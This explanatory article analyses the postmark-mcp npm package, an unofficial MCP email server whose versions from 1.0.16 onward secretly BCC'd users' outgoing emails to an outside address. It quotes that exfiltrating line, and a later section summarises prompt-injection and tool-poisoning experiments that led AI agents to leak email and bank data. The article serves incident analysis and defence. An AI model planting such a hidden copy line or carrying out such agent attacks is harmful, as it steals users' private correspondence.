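# The postmark-mcp npm package that secretly copied users' emails, September 2025

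## What happened: the package, its discovery and its removal

The unofficial software package postmark-mcp let AI assistants send email through the Postmark service. On 17 September 2025 its publisher, under the account name phanpak, released a new version that secretly sent a copy of outgoing messages to an outside address. The security company Koi reported the copying on 25 September, and by that day the package was no longer on npm, the public registry where phanpak had published it.

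Programmers use npm to install packages of ready-made JavaScript code. Publishing a package takes an account and one command, according to Semgrep's *So the first malicious MCP server has been found on npm* (2025), and anyone can publish under any unclaimed name. Postmark is an email delivery service owned by the software company ActiveCampaign. Businesses use it to send password resets, receipts, newsletters and similar emails from their own software.

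MCP, the Model Context Protocol, is an open standard that lets AI assistants use outside tools and data sources. Anthropic, the maker of the chatbot Claude, introduced it in November 2024. An MCP server is a program that offers tools to an assistant. Despite the name, it often runs on the user's own computer with the user's credentials. If someone with an MCP server for Postmark asks an assistant to email a colleague, the assistant passes the recipient, subject and text to the server, which sends the message to Postmark for delivery.

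### The genuine server and the copy

Postmark had written its own MCP server some months earlier. Postmark's *Teaching AI to speak email with our new MCP server* presented it as an experimental early release with four tools for sending messages, sending from templates, listing templates and fetching delivery statistics. The code was on GitHub, and Ecosyste.ms' *Postmark MCP Server*, a catalogue entry for the project, dates the repository to 5 June 2025. Users were meant to download the repository and run the server from a local folder. Postmark had not published the server on npm, so phanpak was able to use the name postmark-mcp there.

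The genuine project carried the MIT licence, which lets anyone copy and republish code, so a copy on npm was not suspicious in itself, but its name was misleading. Digitpatrox's *Unofficial Postmark MCP npm silently stole users’ emails*, a repost of a story by the news site BleepingComputer, describes the package as a perfect replica in code and description that looked like an official port. The phanpak account had 31 other packages on npm, so it did not look like a throwaway.

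The GitHub project was little known. Ecosyste.ms recorded one star (a user's bookmark) in late June, and Dave Ferguson of the security company ReversingLabs counted two after the incident. If the package gained trust by association, that trust more likely came from Postmark's name than from the project.

Along with the code, phanpak copied its author's name. The files of the malicious version 1.0.18, which the security company Snyk reproduced in full, list Jabal Torres as the author. A package's author field is plain text and is copied with the rest of the files. Infosecurity Magazine's *Malicious AI Agent Server Reportedly Steals Emails* explains that Torres works for Postmark and created the genuine project. Torres had no part in publishing the npm package, which was uploaded from phanpak's account.

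### Two days of clean versions

Snyk's *Malicious MCP Server on npm postmark-mcp Harvests Emails* (2025) gives the fullest dated account. Snyk dates version 1.0.0 to 15 September 2025 and version 1.0.18, the last one it noted, to 17 September, with a rapid run of releases in between. The Hacker News dates version 1.0.16 to 17 September as well. Koi found that the versions up to 1.0.15 worked as advertised and did nothing else. Version 1.0.16 added a single line that put an outside address in the BCC field, which hid it from the other recipients. The line was still there in 1.0.18.

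All the clean versions therefore appeared within about two days. Records at ReversingLabs, which scans published packages, support this. ReversingLabs' *postmark-mcp v1.0.9*, in a snapshot from 29 September, gives that version's age as 14 days and reports no evidence of tampering. The company's page for the malicious release, *postmark-mcp v1.0.18*, gives an age of 12 days. Both pages place the malware report three days earlier, so they probably date from the same day. If so, the two releases were two days apart.

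According to the registry dates, the package was ten days old when Koi published its report, and no version that secretly copied emails had existed for more than eight days. Many readers took a different story from the coverage. Koi wrote of a tool that had become part of developers' daily work, and warned that a tool "can be completely legitimate for months" before it turns malicious. Koi phrased the warning as a general pattern, but BeyondMachines then reported as fact that the publisher had maintained the legitimate server "for 15 versions over several months", which the registry dates rule out.

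The count of fifteen versions is accurate or nearly so (1.0.0 to 1.0.15 would make sixteen, if phanpak released every number). But it is a poor measure of time, because a developer fixing small faults can easily publish fifteen versions in a weekend. Postmark later said the culprit "built trust over 15 versions". That may describe the intention, but two days is not long for anyone to come to trust a package.

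Snyk's post is inconsistent about when the package was modified. Its opening sentence gives 25 September, the date of the disclosure, but its timeline lists the last release on 17 September.

### Discovery and removal

Koi sells a product that watches software packages for changes in behaviour. Koi says this product flagged postmark-mcp when version 1.0.16 appeared, and that its researchers then examined the code and found the added line. Koi does not date these events, but it writes that the system caught the change "the moment" the new version introduced it. Read literally, that would mean 17 September, eight days before the report. The Stack's *Postmark MCP dupe was quietly sending emails to a third-party* says Koi flagged "an update on September 17", but the date could refer to the update or to the flagging. The gap between detection and public report could be anything from a few hours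 to eight days.

Before publishing, Koi wrote to phanpak and received no answer. It also reported the package to npm. BleepingComputer also sent questions to phanpak, got no reply, and noted that the package disappeared the day after it wrote. Snyk found the package missing on 25 September, so BleepingComputer must have written by the 24th, and phanpak knew by then that outsiders had noticed.

Koi, BleepingComputer and The Hacker News all say that phanpak deleted the package. Snyk wrote only that the package's removal had probably followed detection. None of the four describes any step taken by npm. Koi interpreted the deletion as an attempt to erase evidence, and its chief technology officer, Idan Dardikman, told Infosecurity Magazine that Koi had already saved what it needed. Koi's interpretation is plausible, but phanpak never explained the deletion or the line of code that copied the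 emails.

Koi's report of 25 September, which called postmark-mcp the first malicious MCP server seen in the wild, set off the press coverage. At 04:14 UTC on 26 September, an entry appeared in OSV, a public database of vulnerable and malicious open-source software. The entry, *Malicious code in postmark-mcp (npm)* (2025), has the identifier MAL-2025-47604 and lists every version from 1.0.16 onwards as affected. Snyk added the package to its own database the same day.

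Postmark said publicly that it had "absolutely nothing to do with this package". The company had not developed or authorised the package, and had not published its MCP server on npm before the incident. It said its email service was unaffected.

An earlier copy of Snyk's *Malicious MCP Server on npm postmark-mcp Harvests Emails* noted that Postmark's genuine GitHub repository had gone offline within about an hour of publication. Snyk said it did not know whether the attack had reached that repository too. The current version of the post still includes that doubt but no longer mentions the outage. Postmark has since gone back to directing users to the same GitHub address. None of these accounts gives a reason for the outage or any sign that an intruder had altered the genuine code.

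### Was the phanpak account hijacked?

Nearly every report treats phanpak as responsible. The exception is NopalCyber's *Malicious postmark-mcp npm Package Allows Email Exfiltration via MCP Ecosystem* (2025), an advisory of 8 October, which advises against trusting even the early versions because the publisher's account "was compromised". If so, phanpak would be a victim, and someone else would have added the line that copied the emails.

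NopalCyber offers no evidence of a compromise. Later in the advisory, it calls the account "attacker-controlled" and says that the account published all the releases and that the author deleted the package after discovery. These details fit a publisher who acted alone, and NopalCyber may have used "compromised" loosely to mean "untrustworthy".

The hijacking theory rests on one unexplained word, and the other public evidence leans mildly against it. The copied emails went to an address at giftshop.club, which Koi thought might be another of the same developer's side projects. The package disappeared soon after Koi and a journalist wrote to phanpak, and no report mentions phanpak claiming to have lost control of the account, as an innocent owner would be expected to do. None of this is proof, since Koi was unsure about the domain and an intruder who controlled the account could also have deleted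 the package.

The motive is also unknown. Dardikman considered possibilities such as money trouble or an offer from a third party, but concluded that nobody could know. Ferguson suggested that the attack may have been only a test, since so few people used the genuine project. Semgrep considered whether the publisher wanted particular emails from a particular user, but expected that the answer would never become known.

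### Installed copies and the later official package

Deleting a package from npm stops new installations but does not affect copies already on people's computers, because npm only supplies the files and the server runs from the user's own disk. Anyone who had version 1.0.16 or later went on sending hidden copies of their emails for as long as they used the program. Many of them would never have chosen that version themselves. *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)*, a November 2025 survey of the protocol's risks, points out that users commonly set such servers to run the latest release, and counts this among the reasons email content leaked without their knowledge.

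The advice from Koi, Snyk and Postmark was much the same:

- Uninstall the package.
- Search email logs for copies sent to giftshop.club.
- Replace any password or access key that had travelled by email while the malicious version was running.

Snyk also recommended replacing the Postmark access token that the server used, blocking the domain, and checking for other packages by phanpak in case they became malicious too.

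Postmark later published its server on npm as @activecampaign/postmark-mcp. In a 2026 post about the server's first year, Postmark described it as an official product that had left the experimental stage and grown from four tools to 24. Some changes concern safety. The server relies on only three outside packages, each fixed to an exact version so that a new release cannot be added unnoticed. It masks email addresses in its logs by default. Labels on its tools identify which actions change or delete something, so that the assistant's software can ask the user before sending a message.

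None of those features would have helped a person who had installed the wrong package, but the name might have. On npm, only accounts that ActiveCampaign authorises can publish under the prefix @activecampaign/, so an outsider could not take a name there as phanpak took postmark-mcp. However, users have to know to look for the prefix. Postmark has added a note at the top of its original announcement asking readers to confirm that they have the official server.

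## What the published code shows

In Snyk's copy of version 1.0.18, the main file is about 400 lines of ordinary JavaScript with comments. The line that copied the emails, `Bcc: 'phan@giftshop.club'`, is just below the recipient field. Semgrep noted that the code was not obfuscated, so anyone who opened the file could have read the address.

### One email, step by step

Suppose a user asks an assistant to email a password-reset link to a customer, ana@example.com. The assistant's software has already started the server on the user's computer. On starting, the server read three things from the user's settings: a default sender address, a default message stream (the Postmark channel that outgoing mail goes through) and the user's Postmark token, a secret key that authorises sending from the user's account. The email then goes through these steps:

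1. The model writes a tool call to sendEmail, giving Ana's address, a subject and the text. The tool also accepts an HTML version, a sender, a tag, a message to reply to and attachments. It has no argument for a BCC.
2. The assistant's software may show this call to the user for approval. The user sees Ana's address, the subject and the text, and approves.
3. The server builds the message. It copies in what the model supplied, fills in the sender and adds the giftshop.club address as a BCC. That address is part of the code, so nothing in the request could change or remove it.
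4. The server passes the message to Postmark with the user's token. Postmark's *Send a single email* lists BCC as an ordinary field, so to Postmark this is a customer's normal request to email two people.
5. Postmark delivers one copy to Ana and one to giftshop.club. Ana's copy does not show the other address.
6. Postmark sends the server a short reply. According to Postmark's *Email API*, the reply has five fields: the recipient, the time, a message ID, an error code and a status message.
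7. The server returns a text to the model with the message ID, Ana's address and the subject. The assistant tells the user that the email has gone to Ana.

The user's approval in step 2 could not have caught the BCC, because the server added it in step 3. A more capable model would not have helped, because the extra address was in neither the model's request nor the server's reply. Passing Postmark's whole reply to the model would not have revealed the address either, because that reply has no BCC field. The server also writes a log on the user's computer, but it contains only the recipient, the subject and the message ID.

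The genuine server now also offers BCC, but as an option the user can request. Postmark lists it among the fields an assistant can add to an email. When the model fills in a BCC address, it appears in the tool call, where the user can see it before approving.

### Why this was not prompt injection or tool poisoning

In a prompt injection, an attacker hides instructions in material the model reads. *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)* gives the example of a customer-support ticket that asks for company logs "to help debug my issue". An assistant that reads the ticket may treat the request as part of its job and upload the logs to the attacker. In tool poisoning, the instructions are in a tool's own description or output. Both attacks work only if the model does something its user did not want.

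The model in the Postmark case did what the user wanted. The descriptions in Snyk's copy of the code are short and accurate, such as "Recipient email address", and contain no hidden instructions. Snyk described the attack as a backdoor in code rather than an attack through prompts. The same line of code would also have worked in a web form where a person typed the email and pressed "send".

Koi correctly writes that the assistant cannot detect the BCC, but it also imagines an assistant obeying a tool's instruction to copy everything to a random address. The code contains no such instruction.

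The survey classifies both malicious code inside a tool and poisoned descriptions as supply-chain attacks, because in both cases the attacker controls the server. That grouping makes sense for deciding whom to trust, but the two attacks leave different traces. A poisoned description is in text that the model reads, while the BCC line was only in the program.

### Which emails the code copied

In version 1.0.18, only one of the server's two sending tools, sendEmail, added the BCC, so Koi's statement that the package copied "every email" is too broad for that version. The sendEmail tool takes a subject and text that the model has written. The other tool, sendEmailWithTemplate, takes the name or number of a template stored at Postmark and details to fill in, such as a customer's name. It builds its message in much the same way, but without the BCC line.

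The tool for sending with templates copied nothing, which matters most for the sensitive messages that the coverage emphasised. Postmark advises programmers who use its JavaScript library to send with templates by default, and says templates work best for operational email, which includes password resets. An assistant that followed this advice would have used the template tool.

Businesses also normally send password resets from their own software, which contacts Postmark directly, so those messages never passed through any version of the MCP server. Ana's email is therefore possible but not typical. The most exposed messages were those that a person asked an assistant to write and send, which could include invoices, internal notes or passwords.

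The server's two remaining tools listed templates and fetched delivery statistics. None of the four tools opened an inbox or retrieved messages sent to the user. Koi's claims that users had given away "full email access" and control of their "entire email flow" therefore go even further beyond what the code shows.

The token allowed more access than the code used. Postmark's *Messages API* shows that a program with such a token can retrieve emails the account has already sent or received, including their text. Another version of the package could have collected weeks of old mail on the day it was installed. Version 1.0.18 makes no such request. It passes the token to Postmark's own library, uses it once more to request statistics from Postmark, and sends it nowhere else. This version therefore did not steal the token, though Snyk's advice to replace it was a sensible precaution.

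The server copies attachments along with the text. When the user or the model supplies a file's web address, the server downloads the file and attaches it to the message before sending, so both recipients get it.

### What the sender's own records show

Senders could find the hidden copies in their own Postmark accounts. The Messages API returns a list of BCC recipients for each sent message. According to Postmark's *A completely redesigned email activity*, the activity page on its website also lists each recipient, including BCCs, with their delivery status. Searching that page for the giftshop.club address would have turned up the copies.

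Postmark keeps these records for only 45 days by default, though customers can choose anything from 7 to 365. With the default setting, the record of an email sent on 17 September expired around 1 November. Someone who first heard of the incident in mid-November could have searched, found nothing and wrongly concluded that nothing had leaked. Postmark also stores only the file names of attachments, so the sender would need the original files to know what had gone out.

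These records might also show whether anyone read the copies, which can't be determined from the code. The server turned on open and click tracking for every message, as the genuine server also does. Postmark stores opens and clicks separately for each recipient, including BCCs, and can add the location and email program used. A victim's account could therefore show that someone had opened a copy sent to giftshop.club or clicked a link in it.

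Open tracking is imperfect evidence that someone read an email. It generally relies on a tiny image in the email, so it misses plain-text messages, and some email programs load images before anyone has looked at the message. A click is better evidence, although security software sometimes follows links automatically. Postmark's statement on the incident does not mention any opens or clicks at the outside address, and it is unknown whether anyone read the stolen emails.

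### How the new version reached users

Users could get version 1.0.16 without choosing it. Assistants usually start an MCP server from a short entry in a settings file, and for npm packages that entry often runs npx, a program that fetches and runs a package. *Postmark MCP*, a catalogue page for the genuine server, recommends this method today. Its sample entry runs npx with the option "-y", which approves the installation in advance, and gives the package name without a version number.

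The malicious package's files also allowed users to run it through npx. With a configuration entry that does this, the assistant's software runs npx each time it starts the server. If npx needs to download the package, npm supplies the release that the publisher has marked as the latest. The new code then starts with the same token and the same four tools, and the user sees no difference.

Not everyone would have moved to the new version at once. Copes (2018) explains in *The npx Node Package Runner* that npx fetches a package only when there is no locally installed copy. A user who had installed version 1.0.12 in a project folder could therefore have stayed on it. Adding "@latest" to the package name, a form that appears in npm's documentation, specifies the newest release.

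Automatic updates probably mattered less than the coverage suggests, because the copying began so soon after the first release. Anyone who first installed the package after 17 September would normally have received the BCC line without any update. *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)* uses the term "rugpull" for a change to a server that people already trust, but this server was only two days old when the copying began.

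### Was version 1.0.16 the same?

All these limits come from version 1.0.18. The copying began in 1.0.16, and there is less evidence about that release. OSV's entry describes its behaviour in one sentence and includes no code. Koi published an image of the added line and said nothing else had changed from 1.0.15. Snyk compared 1.0.15 with 1.0.18 and found that the BCC was the only notable change, although its excerpt also includes a harmless line that sets the reply address to the sender's.

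If both companies are right, versions 1.0.16 and 1.0.18 were nearly identical. But Koi found the BCC on line 231, while in Snyk's copy it is on line 177 and line 231 is part of the code that downloads attachments. Koi may have counted lines in a view that showed old and new code together, or 1.0.16 may have been laid out differently. It is therefore not certain that 1.0.16 also left template emails uncopied.

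The version numbers inside Snyk's copy do not match either. The package file, which holds the name and version, gives 1.0.14, and the main file gives 1.0.0 in two places. Probably nobody updated the 1.0.0. The 1.0.14 is odder, because npm's publishing command normally takes the version from the package file. Snyk does not comment on the mismatch, which could be due to careless publishing or a mix-up when Snyk copied the files.

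The package may also have differed from the genuine server by more than one line. Koi wrote that phanpak took Postmark's code and added the BCC. But the malicious version could also attach files and reply within an existing email thread, and neither feature appears in Postmark's instructions for its own sendEmail tool. Either the genuine code had these features and Postmark had not documented them, or phanpak added them to the copy.

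### What the code suggests about motive

Koi, Snyk and Postmark all treat the BCC as deliberate theft. Snyk wrote that the publisher built the backdoor "with intention to harvest" emails. Several facts support this. The copies went to an outside address, the BCC field hid that address from the other recipients, the package used the name of another company's product, and the tool's descriptions didn't mention the copying.

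Ferguson's suggestion that the attack was only a test also fits the code. Adding one line to one of the two sending tools would be enough to find out whether copies arrived and whether anybody noticed. However, no direct evidence of a test has appeared.

A third possibility is that phanpak added the line for personal use and published it by mistake. This explanation does not appear in any of the reports, and the only support for it is that it is consistent with the code. An email sent through Postmark does not normally appear in the sender's "Sent" folder, so a developer trying out a tool might well add their own address as a BCC to keep a copy. The address begins with "phan", like the account name, which would be a strange choice for a thief who wanted to stay hidden. A thief who wanted every email would also have had good reason to add the line to the template tool, which does not contain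 it.

Theft is more likely than an honest mistake, though phanpak's behavior is stronger evidence of it than the code is. The line was still there in 1.0.18, so phanpak published it more than once. If strangers were using the package, copies of their emails would have started arriving at the giftshop.club address, and the mistake would have been hard to miss for anyone who checked that mailbox. When Koi wrote, phanpak could have said it was a mistake, but didn't reply and deleted the package.

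## How many people were affected

Nobody has published a count of the people whose emails the package copied. Most reports use Koi's rough estimate of 300 organisations and 3,000 to 15,000 emails a day. Koi based this estimate on the package's npm download count, but automated systems probably made many of those downloads.

### The download figures

Koi wrote that postmark-mcp was "downloaded 1,500 times every single week", while The Hacker News gave a total of 1,643 downloads. The package was online for only about ten days, so Koi's figure must describe one week, though "every single week" made the new package sound established.

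Both figures cover all versions, including the clean ones before 1.0.16, but Digitpatrox's repost of the BleepingComputer story gives about 1,500 downloads for the malicious version alone. None of the reports breaks the count down by version.

The download count also differs from the number of people who downloaded the package. npm's *numeric precision matters*, a blog post from 2014, explains that npm adds one to the count each time its servers successfully send a package file, whoever requested it. The total therefore includes downloads by build servers (machines that assemble and test software automatically), mirrors that keep copies of the registry, and robots that download every package for analysis. npm recommended the numbers only as a rough guide to popularity.

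The download count can also miss people. Computers usually keep a copy of a downloaded package, and reinstalling from that copy doesn't add to the count. A company with its own npm mirror could download the package once and distribute it to many developers.

### Koi's estimate

Koi introduced its calculation with the words "We can only guestimate the impact". It has five steps:

| Step | Koi's figure | Basis |
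|---|---|---|
| Downloads per week | 1,500 | npm's count |
| Share in active use | 20% | Guess |
| Organisations | 300 | 20% of 1,500 |
| Emails per organisation per day | 10 to 50 | Guess |
| Emails copied per day | 3,000 to 15,000 | 300 × 10 and 300 × 50 |

Only the first row is a measurement. To estimate 300 organisations from it, Koi had to count each active download as a separate organisation. But a developer who tried five releases in two days could account for five downloads, and several colleagues at one company could each download the package.

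Koi called its 20% assumption conservative but gave no data for it. Elsewhere in the same post, it dropped the assumption, writing of "1,500 users" who trusted the developer and saying that every one of the 1,500 weekly downloads was still compromised. Koi also wrote, without a source, that developers had built the package into hundreds of workflows, which may just restate its estimate of 300.

The estimate of emails per day could be too high or too low. Someone trying out a tool that was a few days old might send two test messages to themselves. A company with an automated agent might send far more than 50, and Snyk warned that agents could have sent large volumes with nobody checking them. At least in version 1.0.18, emails sent from templates were not copied.

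Koi also did not subtract downloads of clean versions. If each of the 19 possible versions from 1.0.0 to 1.0.18 had received an equal share of the 1,643 downloads, the three malicious ones would account for about 259, and Koi's 20% would give about 52 active copies instead of 300. The equal split is only an illustration. It may undercount downloads of the malicious versions, because 1.0.18 was the newest release for about eight days and most people who installed the package during that time would have received it.

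### How the estimate changed in retelling

Security Boulevard's *Malicious MCP Server Found Quietly Stealing Emails* (2025) repeated Koi's result and the assumptions behind it, but stated as fact that thousands of emails were still going to giftshop.club. ITPro's *A malicious MCP server is silently stealing user emails* quoted the daily figure but left out Koi's admission that it was a guess. Techzine's *Malware in MCP server reveals fundamental security problem* reported that about 300 organisations "were affected" and that the copying had gone on for months.

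Infosecurity Magazine reported that 300 organisations were about 20% of "the 15,000 users" who had downloaded the server, but 20% of 15,000 is 3,000. The 15,000 may be 1,500 with an extra zero, or it may come from the top of the email range. BeyondMachines made the same mistake, giving "15,000 total downloads", about nine times the total in The Hacker News.

In *AI-Assistant MCP Downloaded 1,500 Times Per Week Found Stealing Emails*, Witts (2025) mistakenly reported Koi's daily guess of 3,000 to 15,000 exposed emails as the total. Over eight days, Koi's daily rate would give 24,000 to 120,000 emails, so the error made the incident look smaller than Koi's assumptions imply. Witts added that the actual scope was unknown and might have been smaller.

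### How many downloads were automatic?

Tenable, a security company that monitors new npm packages, kept finding brand-new packages with high download counts within hours of their release. Those packages also had unusually many versions. Tenable suspected that publishing a version was enough to trigger downloads, and tested this with three packages of its own, releasing many versions of each. Tenable's *Download pumping*, published in May 2026, gives the average number of downloads per version:

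- 135.55 for a package in which only the version number changed.
- 141.91 for a package with a postinstall script, a command that runs automatically when someone installs the package.
- 158.16 for a package whose postinstall script changed with every version.

Attackers often use postinstall scripts to start malware, so Tenable expected security scanners to download the second and third packages more often. The results matched this expectation, though the differences were modest. None of the packages had real users. The downloads came from mirrors, scanners and analysis bots that fetch new releases as they appear.

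Automated traffic alone could account for all 1,643 downloads of postmark-mcp. The package had at most 19 versions, and with 19 it would have averaged about 86 downloads per version, well below all three of Tenable's averages. Tenable's plainest test package is the closest match, because Snyk's copy of the package file contains no postinstall script. At that test package's rate, 19 versions would draw about 2,575 downloads, over 900 more than postmark-mcp got. If phanpak skipped some version numbers, postmark-mcp's average would be higher, but with at least 13 releases it would still be below the test package's average of about 135.

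This is an inference, because Tenable did not examine postmark-mcp and automated systems may have downloaded new releases at a different rate in September 2025. Tenable's own real-world example, a package called ambar-src, suggests a lower rate. The attackers uploaded 428 harmless versions in two hours, which made the package look busy and well maintained. Three days later, when it already had more than 30,000 downloads, they added malicious code. They published 724 versions in all and reached about 50,000 downloads, or roughly 69 per version.

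At that rate, 19 versions of postmark-mcp would have drawn about 1,300 automated downloads, leaving about 330 by people, build servers and anything else. The ambar-src rate may be a poor guide to a package with so few releases, since some bots may not have kept up with hundreds of versions in two hours. Still, Tenable's experiment can't rule out a few hundred ordinary downloads.

There is no sign that phanpak inflated the count on purpose. Nineteen is a small number of versions compared with 724, and there are easier ways to inflate downloads. Tenable added 17,000 downloads to a test package in about an hour by repeatedly requesting its file from an office laptop. Someone using that method to fake popularity would probably not have stopped at 1,643.

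Daily download counts would be better than the total for judging how much of the traffic was automated. According to npm, mirrors usually download a version on the day it comes out, and phanpak published all the known versions between 15 and 17 September. A spike on those days with few downloads afterwards would suggest automated traffic, while steady downloads over the following week would be harder to attribute to it.

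The two published figures are so close that nearly all the downloads must have fallen within the week covered by Koi's figure of 1,500, but Koi does not say which week that was. If it began on 15 September, it included all the releases, and automated downloads would explain most of the traffic. If it began on 18 September, only about 140 downloads came while phanpak was publishing new versions, and most of the traffic needs another explanation.

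### Evidence of actual victims

Even if bots made nearly all the downloads, a few people could still have installed the package, and a single busy user could have leaked a lot of email. Koi, Snyk, Postmark and the press reports don't name any victims or say how many were confirmed, and no later count has surfaced. Semgrep, writing a week after the disclosure, discussed only what the attack could have exposed.

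Some security companies and databases nevertheless describe the theft as established. PointGuard AI's *Fake Postmark MCP Server Supply Chain Attack* lists "confirmed data exfiltration" among its key points. PromptRiskDB's *Poisoned Postmark MCP Server Email Exfiltration*, an entry in a catalogue of AI security incidents, states that the attacker "successfully exfiltrated emails", but names no victim and gives no number. The published code shows that the server would copy any email sent through it, but not whether anyone sent one. Koi reported finding the line of code but did not report seeing a stolen message.

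The lack of a named victim is only weak evidence that there were none. A company would have had to learn of the incident, search its records and find the copied emails. It might then have told only the affected customers. It is unclear whether any company filed a breach notice over the package.

A few indirect signs suggest that use was low. The genuine GitHub project had two stars and, by the count of Ferguson of ReversingLabs, one watcher, an account that had signed up for updates. That suggests little demand for such a tool, although people who found the copy on npm may never have visited GitHub. ReversingLabs' page for version 1.0.9 lists no other packages that depended on it. This is weaker evidence, because people normally run an MCP server directly instead of building it into another package.

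Semgrep also observed that developers generally avoid packages that are brand new or have few downloads. postmark-mcp was two days old when the copying began. But its download count may have reassured some people if they mistook automated downloads for users.

All this makes 300 organisations hard to believe. A handful of real users, or none at all, would fit the public evidence better.

### Records that could settle the number

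For some other incidents involving MCP servers, the number of affected customers or projects is known. *MCP Security Best Practices After the Mittwald Breach* (David, 2026) describes an attacker who exploited a flaw in the German web host Mittwald's MCP server to read customers' session tokens, the temporary keys that keep a user logged in. Mittwald reported that 56 customer projects were affected. It offered the server itself, so it could investigate its own systems. The postmark-mcp package ran on its users' computers, where neither Koi nor npm could see what it sent.

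Postmark was better able to count those affected, because every hidden copy went out through its service. In late September 2025, a search of all customers' sending logs for the giftshop.club address could have shown how many accounts had sent copies and how many emails were copied. Postmark's statement asked users to check their own logs, but it gave no total and did not mention a wider search, so it is unknown whether Postmark did one.

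Most of those logs should be gone by now. Postmark lets customers keep message records for at most 365 days, so records of emails sent before the package left npm would have expired by 25 September 2026. Copies might survive if a customer saved its message history in its own database before the records expired. Postmark's *How long are Inbound and Outbound messages stored in activity?* describes this option.

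Postmark permanently keeps records of failed deliveries, called bounces. If the giftshop.club address stopped accepting mail while a customer was still running the malicious version, the failed copies could still appear in that customer's account. These records would identify some users who kept the package, but not those who removed it while the address still worked.

Investigators could learn more about how many people were affected from the mailbox that received the copies. Every copy that Postmark delivered went to that one address, so the messages there would show the senders, dates and contents. Some might be phanpak's own tests. Whoever controls the mailbox could have deleted everything in it, and no report mentions an investigator gaining access.

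## What the case showed about the risks of MCP servers

Security companies agreed that postmark-mcp was malicious but disagreed about how much MCP itself was to blame. Koi argued that MCP has "no built-in security model" and that AI agents make a bad tool more harmful by using it hundreds of times a day without review. A week later, Semgrep wrote that MCP is "simple by design" rather than insecure by design, and that the attacker had used methods already seen on npm. Both companies have a commercial interest in the question. Koi offers a product that blocks suspicious packages, while Semgrep sells code scanning and provides it to AI coding tools through MCP.

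### Was MCP to blame?

Koi's strongest point is that people give strangers' programs a lot of access. MCP doesn't limit what a server can do on the user's computer. According to *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)*, Claude Desktop, Cursor and similar assistants by default run servers without a sandbox, which would restrict their access to files and the network. A malicious server can therefore read the user's files and stored credentials. Many users are not programmers and may think they are just connecting an assistant to Slack when they are running a stranger's code.

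Koi also said that MCP servers bypass company checks such as software inventories and email gateways. The incident supports the point about gateways, because Postmark sent the hidden copies from its own systems and they never passed through the victim's mail server.

Koi's complaint about the missing sandbox applies less well to this case. The package sent each copy in the same request as the email itself, so a sandbox that let the email through would also have let the copy through. A sandbox could, however, have restricted a more intrusive version that searched for files.

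Repeated use without review is a risk with ordinary software too. If a web shop sends its receipts through a malicious npm library, the bad line runs for every customer with no AI involved. Dhaval Shah of ReversingLabs, like Koi, raised this risk about MCP servers, saying that a single bad line in one runs hundreds of times a day with nobody checking.

Semgrep's best argument is that the decisive steps happened outside MCP. Phanpak took a name that nobody had claimed on npm, and anyone who installed the package trusted that name. Stricter authentication in the protocol would not have helped, because users gave the server a valid token themselves.

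Research has also traced most accidental flaws to individual programs. *Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities* (He, Patel and Wang, 2026) confirmed 24 publicly disclosed flaws in MCP software up to February 2026. It attributed 18 to programs that failed to check their input properly and three to gaps in the protocol, with some overlap. The BCC in postmark-mcp was deliberate, so this count is more relevant to MCP's general security than to this case.

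Semgrep conceded much of Koi's point, however, writing that MCP had no security controls beyond the user's choice to run a server and any access key the server needed. Both companies described the same gap, but Koi considered it a fundamental fault, while Semgrep considered it a drawback of keeping the protocol simple.

MCP changed who was exposed to an old npm trick. A JavaScript project normally has a lockfile, which records the exact version of each package, and a programmer who can inspect changes. An AI assistant's settings, however, may name a server without specifying a version, and the person who added it may not be a programmer. Dave Ferguson of ReversingLabs called the attack unsophisticated but the use of an MCP server "a new wrinkle". That assessment fits the evidence better than Koi's conclusion that MCP's entire model is broken.

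### Was it the first malicious MCP server?

Researchers had built malicious MCP servers months before Koi announced the first one in the wild. Invariant Labs' *MCP Security Notification* (2025), published on 1 April, describes an experiment that connected the coding assistant Cursor to a trusted email server and to a malicious server that supposedly added numbers. The agent didn't need to call the malicious tool, because hidden instructions in the tool's description were enough to make it send every email to the attacker's address, even when the user had named someone else.

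In *Trivial Trojans*, Croce and South (2025) added fewer than 25 lines to an example weather server from Anthropic's documentation. The altered server got Claude to read one author's real bank balance through a separate banking server and send it to an outside address. The setup took under two hours and cost nothing.

In both experiments, the researchers attacked only themselves. Koi's claim is therefore reasonable if "first" means the first publicly reported malicious server that strangers could install. Earlier ones may have existed, and Koi asked how many other servers were already compromised.

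The best earlier search could easily have missed a malicious server like postmark-mcp. Li and Gao (2025), in *A First Look at the Security Issues in the Model Context Protocol*, scanned servers from four public directories and found 18 with suspicious tool descriptions. Most were demonstrations, and the rest were apparently due to carelessness rather than malice. Li and Gao looked for misleading descriptions and accidental flaws, and did not run this scan on the npm packages in their study, so a server with accurate descriptions and one malicious line of code would probably have passed.

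The incident confirmed that somebody would publish a malicious MCP server, but it was not evidence that criminals were using the techniques from the laboratory experiments. Those techniques depended on a model following hidden instructions, and postmark-mcp contained none. Josh Devon, a co-founder of the security company Flashpoint, was therefore only partly right when he told ReversingLabs that the incident moved the threat from theory to a real attack.

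### How common are the conditions for such an attack?

Li and Gao collected 67,057 server listings from six registries in late June and early July 2025, more than two months before phanpak published postmark-mcp. The number of distinct servers is smaller because some listings point to the same code.

A search of npm found 408 groups of MCP packages whose names differed only in an added beginning or ending, such as "-mcp" or "-mcp-server". In about 329 of these groups (80.6%), the packages belonged to different developers. A user who half remembers a name could easily install the wrong one.

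These figures measure the opportunity for deception. Two honest developers can choose similar names for servers that connect to the same service, and Li and Gao did not report that any of the 408 groups contained a malicious package. Their method would also have missed postmark-mcp, because it compared npm packages with one another and the genuine Postmark server was only on GitHub. phanpak's package also had exactly the same name as the genuine server.

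Li and Gao also found existing listings that attackers could take over. In the four directories, 212 listings pointed to deleted GitHub accounts whose names anyone could register again. Another 304 depended on old account names that anyone could claim after their owners had switched to new ones. Whoever claimed one of these names could put new code behind the listing. Li and Gao did not report that anyone had done so.

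A listing in the official MCP registry is also weak evidence of safety. *Securing the Model Context Protocol (MCP)* explains that a developer only has to prove control of a GitHub repository or a web domain. Nobody has to review the code or scan it for malware. Phanpak could have met the proof-of-control requirement with their own repository. npm, where phanpak published the package, did not require even that proof.

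The same paper gives an example similar to Postmark's. When its three authors wrote it, Slack had no official MCP server, but PyPI, the main public registry for Python packages, had two unofficial ones, slack-mcp-server and slack-mcp-server-v2. Users could mistake either for Slack's own. The authors do not allege wrongdoing in either case. They work for Vanta, MintMCP and Darktrace, which have security or compliance products, and they recommend that organisations set up private registries of approved servers.

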